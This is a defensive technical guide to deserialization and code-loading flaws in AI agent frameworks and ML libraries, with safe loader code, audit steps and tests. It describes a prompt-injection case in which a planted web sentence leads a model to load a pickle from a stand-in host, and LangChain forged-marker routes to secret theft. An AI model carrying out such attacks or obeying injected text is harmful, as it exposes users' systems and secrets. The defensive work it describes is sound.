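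A PyYAML version number doesn't always show whether an installation has the FullLoader flaws. Ubuntu added the fix for CVE-2020-14343 to its PyYAML 5.3.1 package in April 2021, according to Launchpad, Ubuntu's development site. SafeLoader doesn't have these flaws in any version, because it never accepted the tags involved.

### An old PyYAML under a newer document library

The FullLoader flaw reappeared years later in docling-core, part of the document-processing application Docling. Developers use Docling to prepare documents for language models. An attacker could exploit CVE-2026-24009 only if all of these were true, according to Averlon's *CVE-2026-24009*:

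- The installed docling-core was version 2.21.0 or later, but earlier than 2.48.4.
- The installed PyYAML was earlier than 5.4.
- The application called `DoclingDocument.load_from_yaml()` on YAML from an untrusted source.

An agent that only used Docling to convert PDFs therefore didn't meet the conditions. Averlon labels the flaw critical but gives it a CVSS score of 8.1, which is in the "high" range. Even a high rating may overstate the risk for most users, since PyYAML 5.4 was about five years old by 2026. But old versions remain in container images and in projects that pin their dependencies.

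Version 2.48.4 of docling-core replaced FullLoader with SafeLoader. Users who cannot upgrade docling-core can upgrade PyYAML instead. Changing the loader is the better long-term fix because docling-core's safety then no longer depends on the user's PyYAML version.

### Whether PraisonAI's agent definitions could run JavaScript

PraisonAI is an open-source framework for running teams of agents. GCVE's *GHSA-32VR-5GCF-3PW2* (2026) describes a flaw in how it reads agent definitions with js-yaml, a YAML library for JavaScript. According to the advisory, someone could upload a definition with the tag `!!js/function`, and loading it would run code on the server. *CVE-2026-39890* (2026), from the vulnerability database OSV, rates the flaw's severity 9.8 and lists PraisonAI 4.5.115 as the fix.

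In js-yaml version 3, `load` accepts function tags by default and `safeLoad` does not, according to js-yaml's *js yaml* page. Version 4.0.0, released in January 2021, moved these tags to a separate package and made `load` safe by default. js-yaml's *migrate_v3_to_v4.md* shows that a program now has to import that package and add its types to restore the old behaviour.

Even in version 3, loading a function tag normally only creates the function, and its code runs if the program later calls it. Before 3.13.1, a crafted file could also cause a call during loading. The advisory's description of code running on loading is wrong for version 4's default settings and too simple for version 3.

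The advisory doesn't give the js-yaml version that PraisonAI used. Its recommended fix offers the `DEFAULT_SAFE_SCHEMA` setting, which exists only in versions before 4.0.0, but also refers to `safeLoad` as a function from an older version. This suggests whoever wrote it had not checked the code against a particular release.

The list of affected packages is also doubtful. It includes PraisonAI's Python package, although the advisory locates the flaw in a TypeScript file. PraisonAI publishes its TypeScript code separately on npm, the JavaScript package index, under different version numbers. Snyk's *praisonai vulnerabilities* dates npm release 1.7.1 to 5 February 2026, two months before the advisory. A later GitLab advisory still lists 1.7.1 as the current npm release, when the main repository had reached 4.6.58. Upgrading the Python package to 4.5.115 therefore could not have changed the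 code npm users were running. None of the nine flaws in GitLab's *Advisories for Npm/Praisonai package* concerns YAML tags.

The evidence doesn't establish that CVE-2026-39890 was exploitable, and the attack in the advisory fails if PraisonAI used js-yaml 4 with default settings. But PraisonAI's TypeScript command line does read YAML workflow files, as its *Workflows CLI Commands* page shows, so installations are worth checking. Running `npm ls js-yaml` lists the versions in a project, and searching for `js-yaml-js-types` shows whether anyone has re-enabled function tags.

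### Configuration that names code

Changing the loader would not have helped with PraisonAI's other YAML problem. Its configuration files can contain an entry like this:

```yaml
tools:
  - module_path: ./my_tools.py
```

SafeLoader reads the path as ordinary text. PraisonAI then did roughly the following with it:

```python
spec = importlib.util.spec_from_file_location("extra_tools", path)
tools = importlib.util.module_from_spec(spec)
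spec.loader.exec_module(tools)  # runs the statements in the file
```

Anyone who could change the configuration and place a Python file next to it could therefore run code. Kai Aizen and Avraham Shemesh reported this flaw in OSV's *PYSEC-2026-2905* (2026). They showed that PraisonAI's developers had already fixed the same kind of flaw three times, in different files:

| Fixed in | Identifier | Code that the fix covered |
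|---|---|---|
| 4.5.128 | CVE-2026-40156 | Automatic loading of a `tools.py` file from the current folder |
| 4.5.139 | CVE-2026-40287 | `tool_resolver.py` and `api/call.py` |
| 4.6.32 | CVE-2026-44334 | `templates/tool_override.py` |
| 4.6.40 | PYSEC-2026-2905 | Two functions in `agents_generator.py` |

From version 4.5.139 on, the developers' main defence was an environment variable, `PRAISONAI_ALLOW_LOCAL_TOOLS`, that has to be set before PraisonAI loads local tool files. They added the check to some of the places that call `exec_module` but missed others. They would probably have needed several fewer releases to fix this if they had searched the whole repository for `exec_module` after the first report.

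Once a user sets the variable for one legitimate tool, the check lets through files from strangers too. Aizen and Shemesh therefore also recommended an allowlist of places PraisonAI may load tools from.

The flaw's severity depended on the setup. Aizen and Shemesh demonstrated it with a local configuration file and scored that case 7.8. They gave 9.8 to a server that accepts configurations from any GitHub repository without authentication. OSV scores the flaw 8.1. Aizen and Shemesh also list prompt injection as a route, in which an agent follows an instruction to load tools from a particular path, but they don't demonstrate it. In their demonstration, the file runs while PraisonAI is still collecting its tools, before it contacts a language model.

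Snyk also lists a flaw in the approval process for PraisonAI's `workflow.yaml` files that let a crafted recipe (a shareable agent setup) run commands.

**Hydra** has the same weakness in a more general form. Hydra is a configuration library that Meta maintains, and its `instantiate` function creates an object from a description such as this:

```yaml
_target_: builtins.len
_args_: [Oslo]
```

Developers mostly use `_target_` to name a class, but `instantiate` accepts any callable. Here it calls `len("Oslo")` and returns 4. `instantiate` behaves the same way whether the description came from YAML, JSON or another data-only format.

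Unit 42's *Remote Code Execution With Modern AI/ML Formats and Libraries* (2026) reports this flaw in three machine-learning libraries. Unit 42 is the research group of Palo Alto Networks. The libraries all passed settings from a downloaded model to `instantiate`:

| Library | Publisher | Where the settings came from | Fix |
|---|---|---|---|
| NeMo | NVIDIA | `model_config.yaml` inside the model archive | Version 2.3.2 (CVE-2025-23304) |
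| Uni2TS | Salesforce | `config.json` in the model repository | July 2025 (CVE-2026-22584) |
| FlexTok | Apple and the Swiss university EPFL | `config.json`, or metadata in the weights file | June 2025 |

Uni2TS and FlexTok kept their weights in a format that cannot contain code, so a scan of the weights for pickles would have found nothing. The flaw had been in NeMo since at least 2020, and more than 700 models on the model-sharing site Hugging Face used NeMo's format in January 2026.

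Unit 42 had found no attacks that used these flaws by December 2025. It also counted over a hundred Python libraries that models on Hugging Face rely on, and almost 50 of them use Hydra in some way. Those libraries deserve a check but are not necessarily vulnerable, since a program can use Hydra without passing untrusted settings to `instantiate`.

Hydra's developers responded with a warning in the documentation and a denylist, which compares `_target_` with the names of dangerous functions. Unit 42 found the denylist trivial to evade, because Python code can often reach the same function by several names. The documentation also warns against relying on the denylist alone. As of January 2026, no Hydra release included the denylist.

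NVIDIA's fix is stronger. NeMo now finds every `_target_` in the settings, including nested ones, and checks that each name begins with the name of a permitted package. It then imports the target and checks the imported object's parent class and the module it came from. The first check limits which modules NeMo imports, and the second catches dangerous functions that are reachable through a permitted package.

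Model repositories can name code in another way, through the `auto_map` entry in a model's configuration.

### Loading a configuration file from outside

A tool rarely needs to let a file name arbitrary Python functions. Usually it offers a few operations, and the file only has to select one:

```yaml
operation: largest
values: [7, 9, 4]
```

A developer can load this in three steps:

1. Limit the size of the file and parse it with a safe loader.
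2. Check the result against a schema, which is a description of the permitted fields and the type and range of each value.
3. Look up the operation in a fixed table that the program contains.

For the file above, the code could look like this:

```python
import yaml

OPERATIONS = {"largest": max, "smallest": min, "total": sum}

def run_job(raw):
    # 1. Limit the size and parse with a safe loader
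    if len(raw) > 10_000:
        raise ValueError("file too large")
    try:
        job = yaml.safe_load(raw)
    except yaml.YAMLError:
        raise ValueError("invalid YAML") from None

    # 2. Check the fields, types and ranges
    if not isinstance(job, dict) or set(job) != {"operation", "values"}:
        raise ValueError("unexpected fields")
    name, values = job["operation"], job["values"]
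    if not isinstance(name, str):
        raise ValueError("operation must be text")
    if not isinstance(values, list) or not 1 <= len(values) <= 1000:
        raise ValueError("expected 1 to 1000 values")
    if any(type(v) not in (int, float) for v in values):
        raise ValueError("values must be numbers")

    # 3. Select the function from a fixed table
    if name not in OPERATIONS:
        raise ValueError("unknown operation")
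    return OPERATIONS[name](values)
```

With the example file, `run_job` returns 9. If the file contains `operation: builtins.len`, it raises an error because the table has no such entry. Nothing in the file can make the program import a module.

The size limit matters because a safe loader can still use too much processor time. INCIBE's *CVE-2026-59870* (2026) describes such a flaw in the code for ordered tables in js-yaml 5.0.0 to 5.2.0. Corgea's *js-yaml* advisory reports that a file of about 2 MB kept the program busy for more than ten seconds. The flaw affects only programs that select js-yaml's YAML 1.1 schema, and version 5.2.1 fixes it. A size limit helps against such flaws, but a small file can sometimes be slow to parse too, so a tool that handles many strangers' files also needs a time limit.

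The schema check has to examine the parsed values, not the text. If a file contains the same field twice, PyYAML silently keeps the last value, so a person or filter that looks only at the first `operation` line could approve a different operation from the one that runs. PyYAML's developers dropped the check for duplicates in 2006 because it didn't work correctly. The code also compares types exactly. PyYAML reads an unquoted `NO` as `False`, which Python treats as a kind of integer, so a `NO` in the list would otherwise count as zero.

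For larger files, a validation library such as Pydantic is more practical than hand-written checks. By default, Pydantic ignores unknown fields and converts some types, so a developer should turn on strict mode and forbid extra fields.

The same checks should apply to the arguments of a tool call. PraisonAI's tool server passed arguments to its tools without enforcing a schema, according to OSV's *PYSEC 2026 2908*. One tool, meant for validating workflow files, accepted any path and returned the YAML parser's error messages, which could contain fragments of the file. The code above replaces the parser's message with its own to avoid exposing file contents this way.

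The fixed table is only as safe as the functions in it. `max`, `min` and `sum` do nothing dangerous with a list of numbers. If a developer adds a function that opens files or fetches web pages, the schema also has to restrict that function's arguments.

Some frameworks need to let users add their own tools. An administrator can install such a tool as a package and add a short name for it to the table. A configuration file from outside can then select the tool by that name, but it cannot supply a path or module name.

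## Tracing untrusted input to the loaders behind an agent's tools

An agent and its installed packages can contain dozens of loaders, but outsiders can usually reach only a few of them, and an audit has to find those few. Tracing backwards from the loaders is quicker than tracing forwards from the inputs, because most programs have far more inputs than loaders.

1. List the loaders in the agent's own code and in its dependencies.
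2. List the inputs that an outsider can shape. These include tool arguments, downloaded files, network messages, shared caches and saved models or agents.
3. Connect the two. For each loader, trace its argument back until it leads either to a constant in the program or to something from step 2.
4. Record the preconditions, such as a particular version, a setting, an open port or a writable folder.
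5. Remove the loader or replace it with a data-only one. If neither is possible, cut off the outsider's access to it.
6. Write a regression test that gives the tool a pickle with a harmless marker call and fails if the call happens.

### Finding the loaders

A text search is a good start:

```
grep -rnE --include="*.py" \
  "pickle|dill|joblib|shelve|torch\.load|recv_pyobj|yaml\.(load|full_load|unsafe_load)|exec_module|instantiate\(|trust_remote_code" \
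  src/ .venv/
```

Searching for `pickle` also finds `cloudpickle`, `jsonpickle`, `read_pickle` and `allow_pickle`. The search will return many matches from the installed packages, so it makes sense to start with packages that read files from outside sources or listen on a network port.

Python's auditing events can show which of these loaders actually run:

```python
import sys, traceback

def report(event, args):
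    if event == "pickle.find_class":
        print(*args)
        traceback.print_stack(limit=8)

sys.addaudithook(report)
```

With this hook in place, running the agent's tests prints the chain of function calls behind each pickle lookup, even one deep inside a dependency. The hook misses code that the tests never run. It also misses pickles of plain values, which need no lookups.

Files that the agent wrote belong in step 2 if another tool can write to the same folder. For example, the developer of one tool may think its cache is internal, while a second tool saves downloads in the same folder.

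### Following a sentence from a web page to `pandas.read_pickle`

Suppose a data-analysis agent has one tool that fetches web pages and another that loads datasets. The second picks a reader by file extension:

```python
from pathlib import PurePosixPath
import pandas as pd

READERS = {
    ".csv": pd.read_csv,
    ".parquet": pd.read_parquet,
    ".pkl": pd.read_pickle,
}

def load_dataset(path):
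    """Load a dataset and summarize its columns."""
    reader = READERS[PurePosixPath(path).suffix.lower()]
    return reader(path).describe().to_string()
```

An attacker could reach the pickle loader like this:

1. A user asks the agent to summarize the rainfall figures on a weather club's website.
2. The agent fetches the page. Someone has added a sentence to it, which claims that the table is incomplete and that the full data is at `https://rain.example/full.pkl`.
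3. The model calls `load_dataset("https://rain.example/full.pkl")`.
4. The extension selects `pandas.read_pickle`, which downloads the file.
5. The pickle loader calls whatever the file names.

If the file is the harmless pickle that calls `len("Oslo")`, `read_pickle` runs the call and returns 4. The tool then fails because a number has no `describe` method, and the user sees an error message about a dataset.

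The added sentence can look harmless, because many legitimate pages link to a fuller dataset. A filter that searches for hostile instructions would have little to detect.

Suppose the same agent also reads PDFs, caches results and has a settings file. Its audit record might look like this:

| Loader | Who can shape its input | Preconditions | Fix |
|---|---|---|---|
| `pandas.read_pickle` in `load_dataset` | Anyone whose text the model reads | The model passes on a path or web address | Remove the reader |
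| `pickle.loads` in pdfminer.six | Anyone who sends a PDF | An old version, and a second file in a known place | Upgrade |
| `joblib.Memory` cache | Anyone who can write to the cache folder | Another tool saves files there | Give the cache a private folder |
| `yaml.safe_load` for settings | Only the developer | None found | None needed |

### The repaired tool and its test

The repaired tool has no pickle reader and opens files from one folder only:

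```python
from pathlib import Path
import pandas as pd

DATA = Path("/srv/agent/data").resolve()
MAX_BYTES = 50_000_000
READERS = {".csv": pd.read_csv, ".parquet": pd.read_parquet}

def load_dataset(name):
    """Summarize a CSV or Parquet file from the data folder."""
    path = (DATA / name).resolve()
    if not path.is_relative_to(DATA) or not path.is_file():
        raise ValueError("not a file in the data folder")
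    reader = READERS.get(path.suffix.lower())
    if reader is None:
        raise ValueError("unsupported file type")
    if path.stat().st_size > MAX_BYTES:
        raise ValueError("file too large")
    with path.open("rb") as f:
        return reader(f).describe().to_string()
```

Removing `.pkl` from the table closes the route to code execution. The other changes limit what else a misled model can do with the tool. A web address now turns into a local path that doesn't exist. The location check has to come after the join, because Python discards the folder when joining it to an absolute path. The tool also opens the file itself, so pandas never interprets the name.

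The size limit applies to the file on disk, but a compressed Parquet file can take up far more memory once loaded, so the process also needs a memory limit. If the team has old pickled datasets, it can convert them to Parquet once, outside the agent. This is only safe for files the team made itself, because converting a pickle means loading it.

The test file defines a marker function that only adds a word to a list:

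```python
import pickle
import pytest
import dataset_tool

calls = []

def marker():
    calls.append("called")

class Marker:
    def __reduce__(self):
        return (marker, ())

PICKLE = pickle.dumps(Marker())

@pytest.fixture(autouse=True)
def reset():
    calls.clear()

def test_marker_works():
    pickle.loads(PICKLE)
    assert calls == ["called"]

@pytest.mark.parametrize("name", ["x.pkl", "x.csv", "x.parquet"])
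def test_tool_refuses_pickle(name, tmp_path, monkeypatch):
    monkeypatch.setattr(dataset_tool, "DATA", tmp_path.resolve())
    (tmp_path / name).write_bytes(PICKLE)
    with pytest.raises(ValueError):
        dataset_tool.load_dataset(name)
    assert calls == []
```

The first test confirms that the marker works under an ordinary pickle loader. Without it, a broken marker would make the second test pass for the wrong reason. The second test checks the list as well as the error, because an unsafe loader can make the call and then raise an error. It also gives the pickle misleading extensions, in case someone later adds a reader that guesses the format from the contents.

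Putting `.pkl` back in `READERS` should make the test fail, which is worth trying once. The tool also needs a test with an ordinary CSV file, because a tool that rejected every file would pass the tests above.

### Files and saved agents that someone has to open

In the rainfall example, the attacker has to mislead the model, but often an attack works if the agent just opens a file during its normal work.

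pdfminer.six is a Python library that extracts text from PDFs, and many document readers depend on it. Chinese, Japanese and Korean fonts use tables called CMaps to match codes with characters, and pdfminer.six stored these tables as pickles. A PDF names the CMap it needs. According to OSV's *Arbitrary Code Execution in pdfminer.six via Crafted PDF Input* (2026), the library built a file path from that name without restricting the path to the library's own folder. A crafted PDF could therefore make the library unpickle any file whose name ended in `.pickle.gz`.

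On Linux and macOS, the attacker also had to get a pickle onto the machine at a path they knew in advance. According to OSV, this is difficult or impossible in many cases. On Windows, the path could point to a network location, so the attacker could host the pickle elsewhere. An agent that saves email attachments under their original names in a fixed folder nearly meets the Linux and macOS condition, because one email can carry both files.

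The first fix, in version 20251107, was incomplete. pdfminer.six still unpickled CMaps from every folder on its search path, and CIRCL's *Insecure Deserialization (pickle) in pdfminer.six CMap Loader* (2025) describes how a user who could write to one of those folders could run code as the account that processed the PDF. Debian's *CVE-2025-70559* page records that version 20251230 replaced the pickles with JSON. In May 2026, that page still listed the packages in Debian's bookworm and trixie releases as vulnerable. The older bullseye release had a fixed package whose version number still began with 20200726, so a check of the version number alone would have wrongly marked it as vulnerable.

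Another package's version limits can also block an upgrade. Unstructured, a library that prepares documents for language models, restricted which versions of pdfminer.six could be installed with it. In January 2026, *Remove pdfminer.six version constraint, bump dependencies to address high severity CVEs* (lawrence-u10d, 2026) removed the restriction to get the security fix. The new version required a change to one of Unstructured's tests.

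**MLflow** is a platform for storing and sharing machine-learning models, and can also store agents built with the LangChain framework. From version 2.5.0, it saved these agents' tools with cloudpickle, and `mlflow.langchain.load_model` unpickled them. An attacker who could upload a model to a shared MLflow server could run code on the machine of anyone who loaded that model, according to HiddenLayer's *Cloudpickle Load on Langchain AgentExecutor Model Load Leading to Code Execution* (2024).

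There was still no fixed version in October 2025, 16 months later, according to Snyk's *Deserialization of Untrusted Data Affecting mlflow package, versions [2.5.0,]* (2024). MLflow can now also store a LangChain model as a Python script instead of a pickle. A script is easier to review, but loading the model still runs the script. With either format, the main protection is to control who can upload models to the server. Anyone with a newer MLflow release can check for the old loader by searching the `langchain` folder for `cloudpickle.load`.

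### Ports that accept pickles

If a program unpickles messages from a network port, an attacker who can connect to that port can attack the program without using the model. Prompt-injection filters and approval prompts don't stop the attack, because the message never passes through them.

**Upsonic**, a framework for building agents, had an `add_tool` endpoint for registering tools. It listened on port 7541 by default and loaded cloudpickle data without asking for a login, so an attacker only needed to be able to reach the port. Arawa's *Upsonic Cloudpickle Deserialization of Untrusted Data Remote Code Execution Vulnerability* page scores the flaw 9.8 out of 10.

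The Zero Day Initiative, which passes researchers' findings on to vendors, reported the cloudpickle flaw to Upsonic on 19 June 2025. It asked for updates in October and November, then published *(0Day) Upsonic Cloudpickle Deserialization of Untrusted Data Remote Code Execution Vulnerability* (2026) on 9 January without a fix. The only mitigation it offered was to restrict access to the product.

Switching to JSON would not be a simple fix here, because cloudpickle is designed to send functions, and an endpoint for new tools may well need to receive them. Upsonic could instead let callers choose from tools that an administrator has already installed. If callers do need to upload code, the endpoint needs a strong login and a sandbox.

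Equixly, which sells an AI testing agent, reports in its article *Can AI identify 0-days?* that the agent found the flaw. The agent sent malformed bytes to the endpoint, and the reply contained the Python error `UnpicklingError: invalid load key`. The agent inferred that the server was loading pickles and confirmed the flaw by sending a pickle with an observable side effect. Equixly argues that traditional scanners would probably have missed the flaw, but reports no comparison with one. Developers can do the first step themselves by sending a few random bytes to each of their own ports and searching the replies and logs for `UnpicklingError`. Hiding the error message from callers makes the flaw harder to find but doesn't fix it.

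GitLab's *CVE-2025-62373* (2026) explains that **Pipecat**, a framework for voice agents, unpickled data from WebSocket clients in its `LivekitFrameSerializer` class. A server was vulnerable only if it used this undocumented, non-default class and accepted connections from outsiders. The flaw affects versions from 0.0.41 up to but not including 0.0.94. MITRE's *CVE-2025-62373* record advises users to both upgrade and switch to `LiveKitTransport`.

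**LeRobot**, Hugging Face's robotics platform, can run the model that controls a robot on a separate server. The server and the robot's client exchanged pickled data without a login or encryption. According to NVD's *CVE-2026-25874* page, an attacker could run code on either one in versions up to 0.5.1.

A researcher first reported the flaw in December 2025. The developers replied in January that this experimental part of the code needed an almost complete rewrite. A second researcher, Valentin Lobstein, published details in April, as The Hacker News (2026) reported. The developers planned a fix for version 0.6.0, and Hugging Face's *LeRobot v0.6.0* (2026) announced that release on 7 July. MONAI's and pdfminer.six's first fixes were incomplete, so users may want to search the installed copy for `pickle.loads` before exposing the port.

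### How one line spread between inference servers

Inference servers, the programs that run language models, often split their work between processes that exchange messages. Many use ZeroMQ, a messaging library. Its Python version has a function, `recv_pyobj()`, that receives a message and unpickles it.

The security company Oligo found this function in Meta's Llama Stack in 2024, on network sockets that required no login. It then found nearly identical code in several other projects, as Oligo Security's *ShadowMQ* describes. Developers had copied files from one project to another, and the vulnerable file in SGLang even began with the words "Adapted from vLLM". The projects responded differently:

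| Project | Identifier | Response |
|---|---|---|
| Meta Llama Stack | CVE-2024-50050 | Replaced pickle with a JSON-based format |
| vLLM | CVE-2025-30165 | Replaced the vulnerable engine with a safe one as the default |
| NVIDIA TensorRT-LLM | CVE-2025-23254 | Added an HMAC check |
| Modular Max Server | CVE-2025-60455 | Replaced pickle with MessagePack |
| SGLang | None | Made incomplete fixes |
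| Microsoft Sarathi-Serve | None | Still vulnerable when Oligo published |

JSON and MessagePack, a compact binary format for similar values, remove the flaw as long as the program doesn't look up names from the messages and call them. An HMAC is a signature made with a secret key that both sides share. If the receiver checks it before loading a message, it blocks messages from anyone without the key, but an attacker who takes over one process and its key can still run code in the others.

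Oligo Security also found thousands of ZeroMQ sockets open to the internet, some of which clearly belonged to production inference servers. The count is an upper limit on the number of vulnerable machines, since a program can use ZeroMQ without pickle.

OffSeq's *LMCache* (2026) page, from October, describes a more recent critical flaw in LMCache, a library that stores intermediate results so that language models can reuse them. In multiprocess mode, versions from 0.3.9 up to but not including 0.5.6 let an outsider run code without logging in.

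An audit should check which ports are open. On Linux, `ss -ltnp` lists the ports that accept TCP connections and the programs listening on them. A port bound to any address other than `127.0.0.1` or `::1` may be reachable from other machines. Even a local port may be exposed if one of the agent's tools sends web requests and the model controls both the address and the contents, because an injected instruction may then be able to send data to a local service that unpickles it.

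### What Bandit, Semgrep and CodeQL find and miss

Static analysers examine source code without running it. With their usual settings, three common ones would probably all miss the flaw in the original `load_dataset`, for different reasons.

**Bandit** compares the names of called functions with a built-in list of risky ones. The list includes `pickle.load` and `pandas.read_pickle`, so Bandit would flag `pd.read_pickle(path)`. But `load_dataset` stores the function in a dictionary and calls it as `reader(path)`, which Bandit misses because that name isn't on the list. Bandit also can't determine whether an outsider controls the argument, so it warns about harmless loads too.

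Developers can be tempted to silence Bandit's warnings. LeRobot's code had `# nosec` comments, which tell Bandit to ignore a line, beside its unsafe loads. Lobstein remarked in The Hacker News that the developers had silenced "the tool that was trying to warn them". Running Bandit with `--ignore-nosec` makes it check those lines anyway.

**Semgrep** searches for code patterns, and developers can write their own. A rule that looks only for calls would miss `load_dataset` just as Bandit does. This one matches any mention of the function:

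```yaml
rules:
  - id: pandas-pickle-reader
    pattern: pandas.read_pickle
    message: This reader can run code from the file
    languages: [python]
    severity: ERROR
```

It also matches `pd.read_pickle`, because Semgrep resolves import aliases. Semgrep can also trace data from an input to a loader, but the free edition does this only within a single function.

**CodeQL** follows data across a whole program, from known untrusted sources to known dangerous functions. It is the best of the three at linking a web request to a `pickle.loads` call several functions away. In `load_dataset`, the untrusted value arrives as an ordinary function argument, which CodeQL doesn't treat as a source unless it has a description of the agent framework that marks tool arguments as untrusted. Developers can write that description themselves, which is probably worth the effort for an agent with many tools.

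Teams usually run these analysers only on their own code, which would leave out pdfminer.six. A dependency scanner such as `pip-audit` partly fills that gap by comparing installed versions with published advisories, but it can't find unreported flaws. No analyser can determine from source code alone whether a firewall blocks a port.

Analysers' rule lists change between releases, so a simple way to check an analyser is to run it on a small file that calls each loader from the audit once directly and once through a dictionary lookup.

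### Deciding what to fix first

A CVSS score describes how severe a flaw is when its preconditions hold. Whether they hold in a particular agent is a separate matter, and usually a more useful one:

| Software | CVSS | What has to happen |
|---|---|---|
| Upsonic | 9.8 | An attacker reaches the port |
| LeRobot | 9.8 | An attacker reaches the port |
| Pipecat | 9.8 | An attacker reaches a server that uses the optional serializer |
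| MLflow | 8.8 | Someone loads the attacker's saved agent |
| pdfminer.six | 8.6 | Someone processes the attacker's PDF, and the pickle is within reach |

Most Pipecat servers probably never used the optional serializer, so the 9.8 score doesn't apply to them. MLflow's score can understate the risk. It is lower partly because a person has to load the model, but an agent with a tool for loading saved agents could do that on its own.

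The US cybersecurity agency CISA adds its own assessments to CVE records, including whether attackers could automate an attack. It judged that they could for Pipecat and LeRobot (MITRE's *LeRobot Unsafe Deserialization Remote Code Execution via gRPC*, 2026), but not for pdfminer.six (MITRE's *CVE-2025-64512*). These judgments largely match the difference between attacking through an open port, which anyone can scan for, and attacking through a file, which has to reach the right machine.

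Attackers exploit only a small share of recorded flaws, and many severe ones go unexploited. Shodan's *Vulnerability Details CVE-2026-25874* page lists an EPSS score of 0.002 for LeRobot's flaw, an estimated 0.2% chance of exploitation within 30 days.

EPSS scores help a team with hundreds of open advisories decide which to fix first. But a low score is a poor reason to leave a reachable loader in place, because EPSS doesn't account for how a particular agent is set up. It also doesn't cover a tool like `load_dataset`, which exists only in one team's code and will never have a CVE number.

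A sensible order is to deal first with loaders that anyone on the internet can reach without logging in, then with those that a stranger's file or web page can reach through the agent. Loaders that need a login or write access to a private folder can usually wait for the next planned release. Ranking isn't worthwhile for fixes that take less time than looking up a score, such as deleting the `.pkl` line in `load_dataset`.

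## Saving and restoring agent state safely

Even an agent's own saved records can be unsafe to load, because they contain text from web pages, emails and tool results, and agent frameworks often save them in formats that can rebuild objects. In 2025 and 2026, researchers found several flaws of this kind in LangChain and LangGraph, two popular open-source frameworks for building agents.

### How markers turn saved data into objects

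Most of what agent frameworks save falls under these headings:

- **Messages** let a user continue a conversation later.
- **Caches** hold the results of earlier steps, so that the agent doesn't have to repeat them.
- **Agent checkpoints** are snapshots of a whole run. LangGraph saves one after each step, so a run can resume after a crash or wait for a person to approve an action.

JSON and MessagePack hold only plain values, but an agent's state also includes objects, such as messages and dates. Frameworks get around this by adding markers that tell the loader to rebuild an object. This small loader uses `$type` as its marker:

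```python
def revive(table):
    if table.get("$type") == "Reading":
        return Reading(table["city"], table["celsius"])
    return table

state = json.loads(raw, object_hook=revive)
```

Python's `json` module passes every JSON object in the text to `revive`, including nested ones. The loader turns `{"$type": "Reading", "city": "Oslo", "celsius": 7}` into a `Reading` and leaves other JSON objects unchanged. `Reading` is the only class it can build, and that class is harmless. If the loader imported whatever module and class the `$type` marker named, it would be about as dangerous as jsonpickle.

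Even a loader limited to harmless classes can misread ordinary data as a type marker. If a weather service's reply contains a `$type` field with the value `Reading`, the agent saves the reply as an ordinary table but gets back a `Reading` when it loads the file. Restricting access to the file or signing it wouldn't help, because nobody has tampered with it. The program has to **escape** such tables when it saves them, for example by putting them in a wrapper that marks the contents as data.

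MessagePack avoids this confusion because it has a separate kind of value for markers, called an extension type. An extension consists of a number and some bytes, and the program can supply a function (a hook) that builds an object from them. An ordinary table never turns into an extension, whatever keys it has. A MessagePack loader is data-only unless it has a hook, in which case its safety depends on what the hook does and who can write the bytes.

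Searching Python code for `object_hook` and `ext_hook` finds many loaders that use markers.

### LangChain's missing escape

LangChain saves its objects as JSON. In simplified form, a message from a model looks like this:

```json
{
  "lc": 1,
  "type": "constructor",
  "id": ["langchain", "schema", "messages", "AIMessage"],
  "kwargs": {"content": "It is 7 degrees in Oslo."}
}
```

The `lc` key marks the table as a LangChain object, `id` identifies the class, and `kwargs` holds the arguments for creating an instance. The loader checks the class against an allowlist before creating the instance. LangChain also has a marker for secrets that contains only the name of a key, which keeps API keys out of saved files. The loader can fill in the value from the process's environment variables.

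LangChain's saving functions, `dumps` and `dumpd`, copied ordinary dictionaries unchanged even if they contained an `lc` key. The loader then treated an outsider's data as a LangChain object if it had the right shape. This flaw, CVE-2025-68664, went unnoticed for two and a half years, according to Cyata (2025), the security company whose researcher found it. The researcher had been auditing the loading code, but the flaw was a line missing from the saving code.

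An attack through a model would go like this:

1. An outsider influences the model through prompt injection.
2. The model's response includes a table in LangChain's format. It ends up in `additional_kwargs` or `response_metadata`, two message fields for extra details about a response.
3. A LangChain function that streams the agent's progress serializes the message and then loads it again.
4. The loader finds the `lc` key and creates an object or looks up a secret.

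OSV's *PYSEC-2026-373* (2026), which reproduces the maintainers' advisory, describes these message fields as the most common attack route. But its example writes the table directly into the program, so it shows the missing escaping but not the model's role in the attack. How much a model's output can influence these fields probably varies between model providers.

The advisory lists 12 affected uses, which this table groups by purpose:

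| Purpose | Affected uses |
|---|---|
| Streaming and logging | `astream_events(version="v1")`; `astream_log()` |
| Direct calls | `dumps()` or `dumpd()` on outsiders' data, followed by `load()` or `loads()`; `load()` or `loads()` on data that an outsider serialized |
| Chat history | `RunnableWithMessageHistory` |
| Caches | The caches in langchain-community |
| Stored documents | `InMemoryVectorStore.load()`; `create_lc_store` or `create_kv_docstore`; `MultiVectorRetriever` with byte stores |
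| Shared objects and past runs | `hub.pull`; `StringRunEvaluatorChain`; `LangSmithRunChatLoader` |

Adding the missing escape protects only data that LangChain itself saves. `hub.pull` downloads shared objects from the LangChain Hub, so someone else supplies the whole record, and safety depends on what the loader permits.

### What the LangChain flaw let an attacker do

The demonstrated harm was leaking secrets. The loader's `secrets_from_env` setting was on by default, so an attacker could forge a secret marker naming any environment variable, and the loader would replace the marker with that variable's value. If the attacker could also see the loaded data, for example in a message history, they could read the secret.

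Cyata also found a way for an attacker to leak secrets without seeing any output. One class on the default allowlist, for Amazon's Bedrock model service, sends a web request as soon as the loader creates an instance of it. An attacker could use the forged record to set the request's address and include an environment variable in it.

Cyata looked for a way to execute code directly through `loads()` but did not confirm one. The closest route used `PromptTemplate`, another permitted class, which accepts Jinja2 templates. These can run Python code when a program fills them in. Loading only creates the template, so the code runs only if the program later fills it in. Cyata suspected that a direct route might exist and asked other researchers for leads.

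Red Hat's *CVE-2025-68664* page goes further, stating that the flaw "allows remote attackers to achieve arbitrary code execution". That doesn't match Red Hat's own severity score of 9.3, which assumes a high impact on confidentiality, a low impact on integrity and none on availability. Arbitrary code execution normally counts as high on all three, which would have raised the score to 10. The evidence supports what the score describes, a serious leak of secrets.

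NVD's score is 8.2. It differs from Red Hat's only because NVD assumes that the damage stays within the vulnerable software. Stolen API keys give access to other systems, so 9.3 seems the better score for most agents.

### LangChain's new defaults

LangChain fixed the flaw in versions 0.3.81 and 1.2.5 of the langchain-core package. If an ordinary dictionary contains an `lc` key, `dumps` now puts it inside a table with the key `__lc_escaped__`. The loader removes the wrapper and returns the contents as plain data. The same releases tightened the loader's defaults:

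| Setting | Old behaviour | New default |
|---|---|---|
| `allowed_objects` | Any serializable class from approved packages | `'core'`, which permits classes from langchain_core |
| `secrets_from_env` | On | Off |
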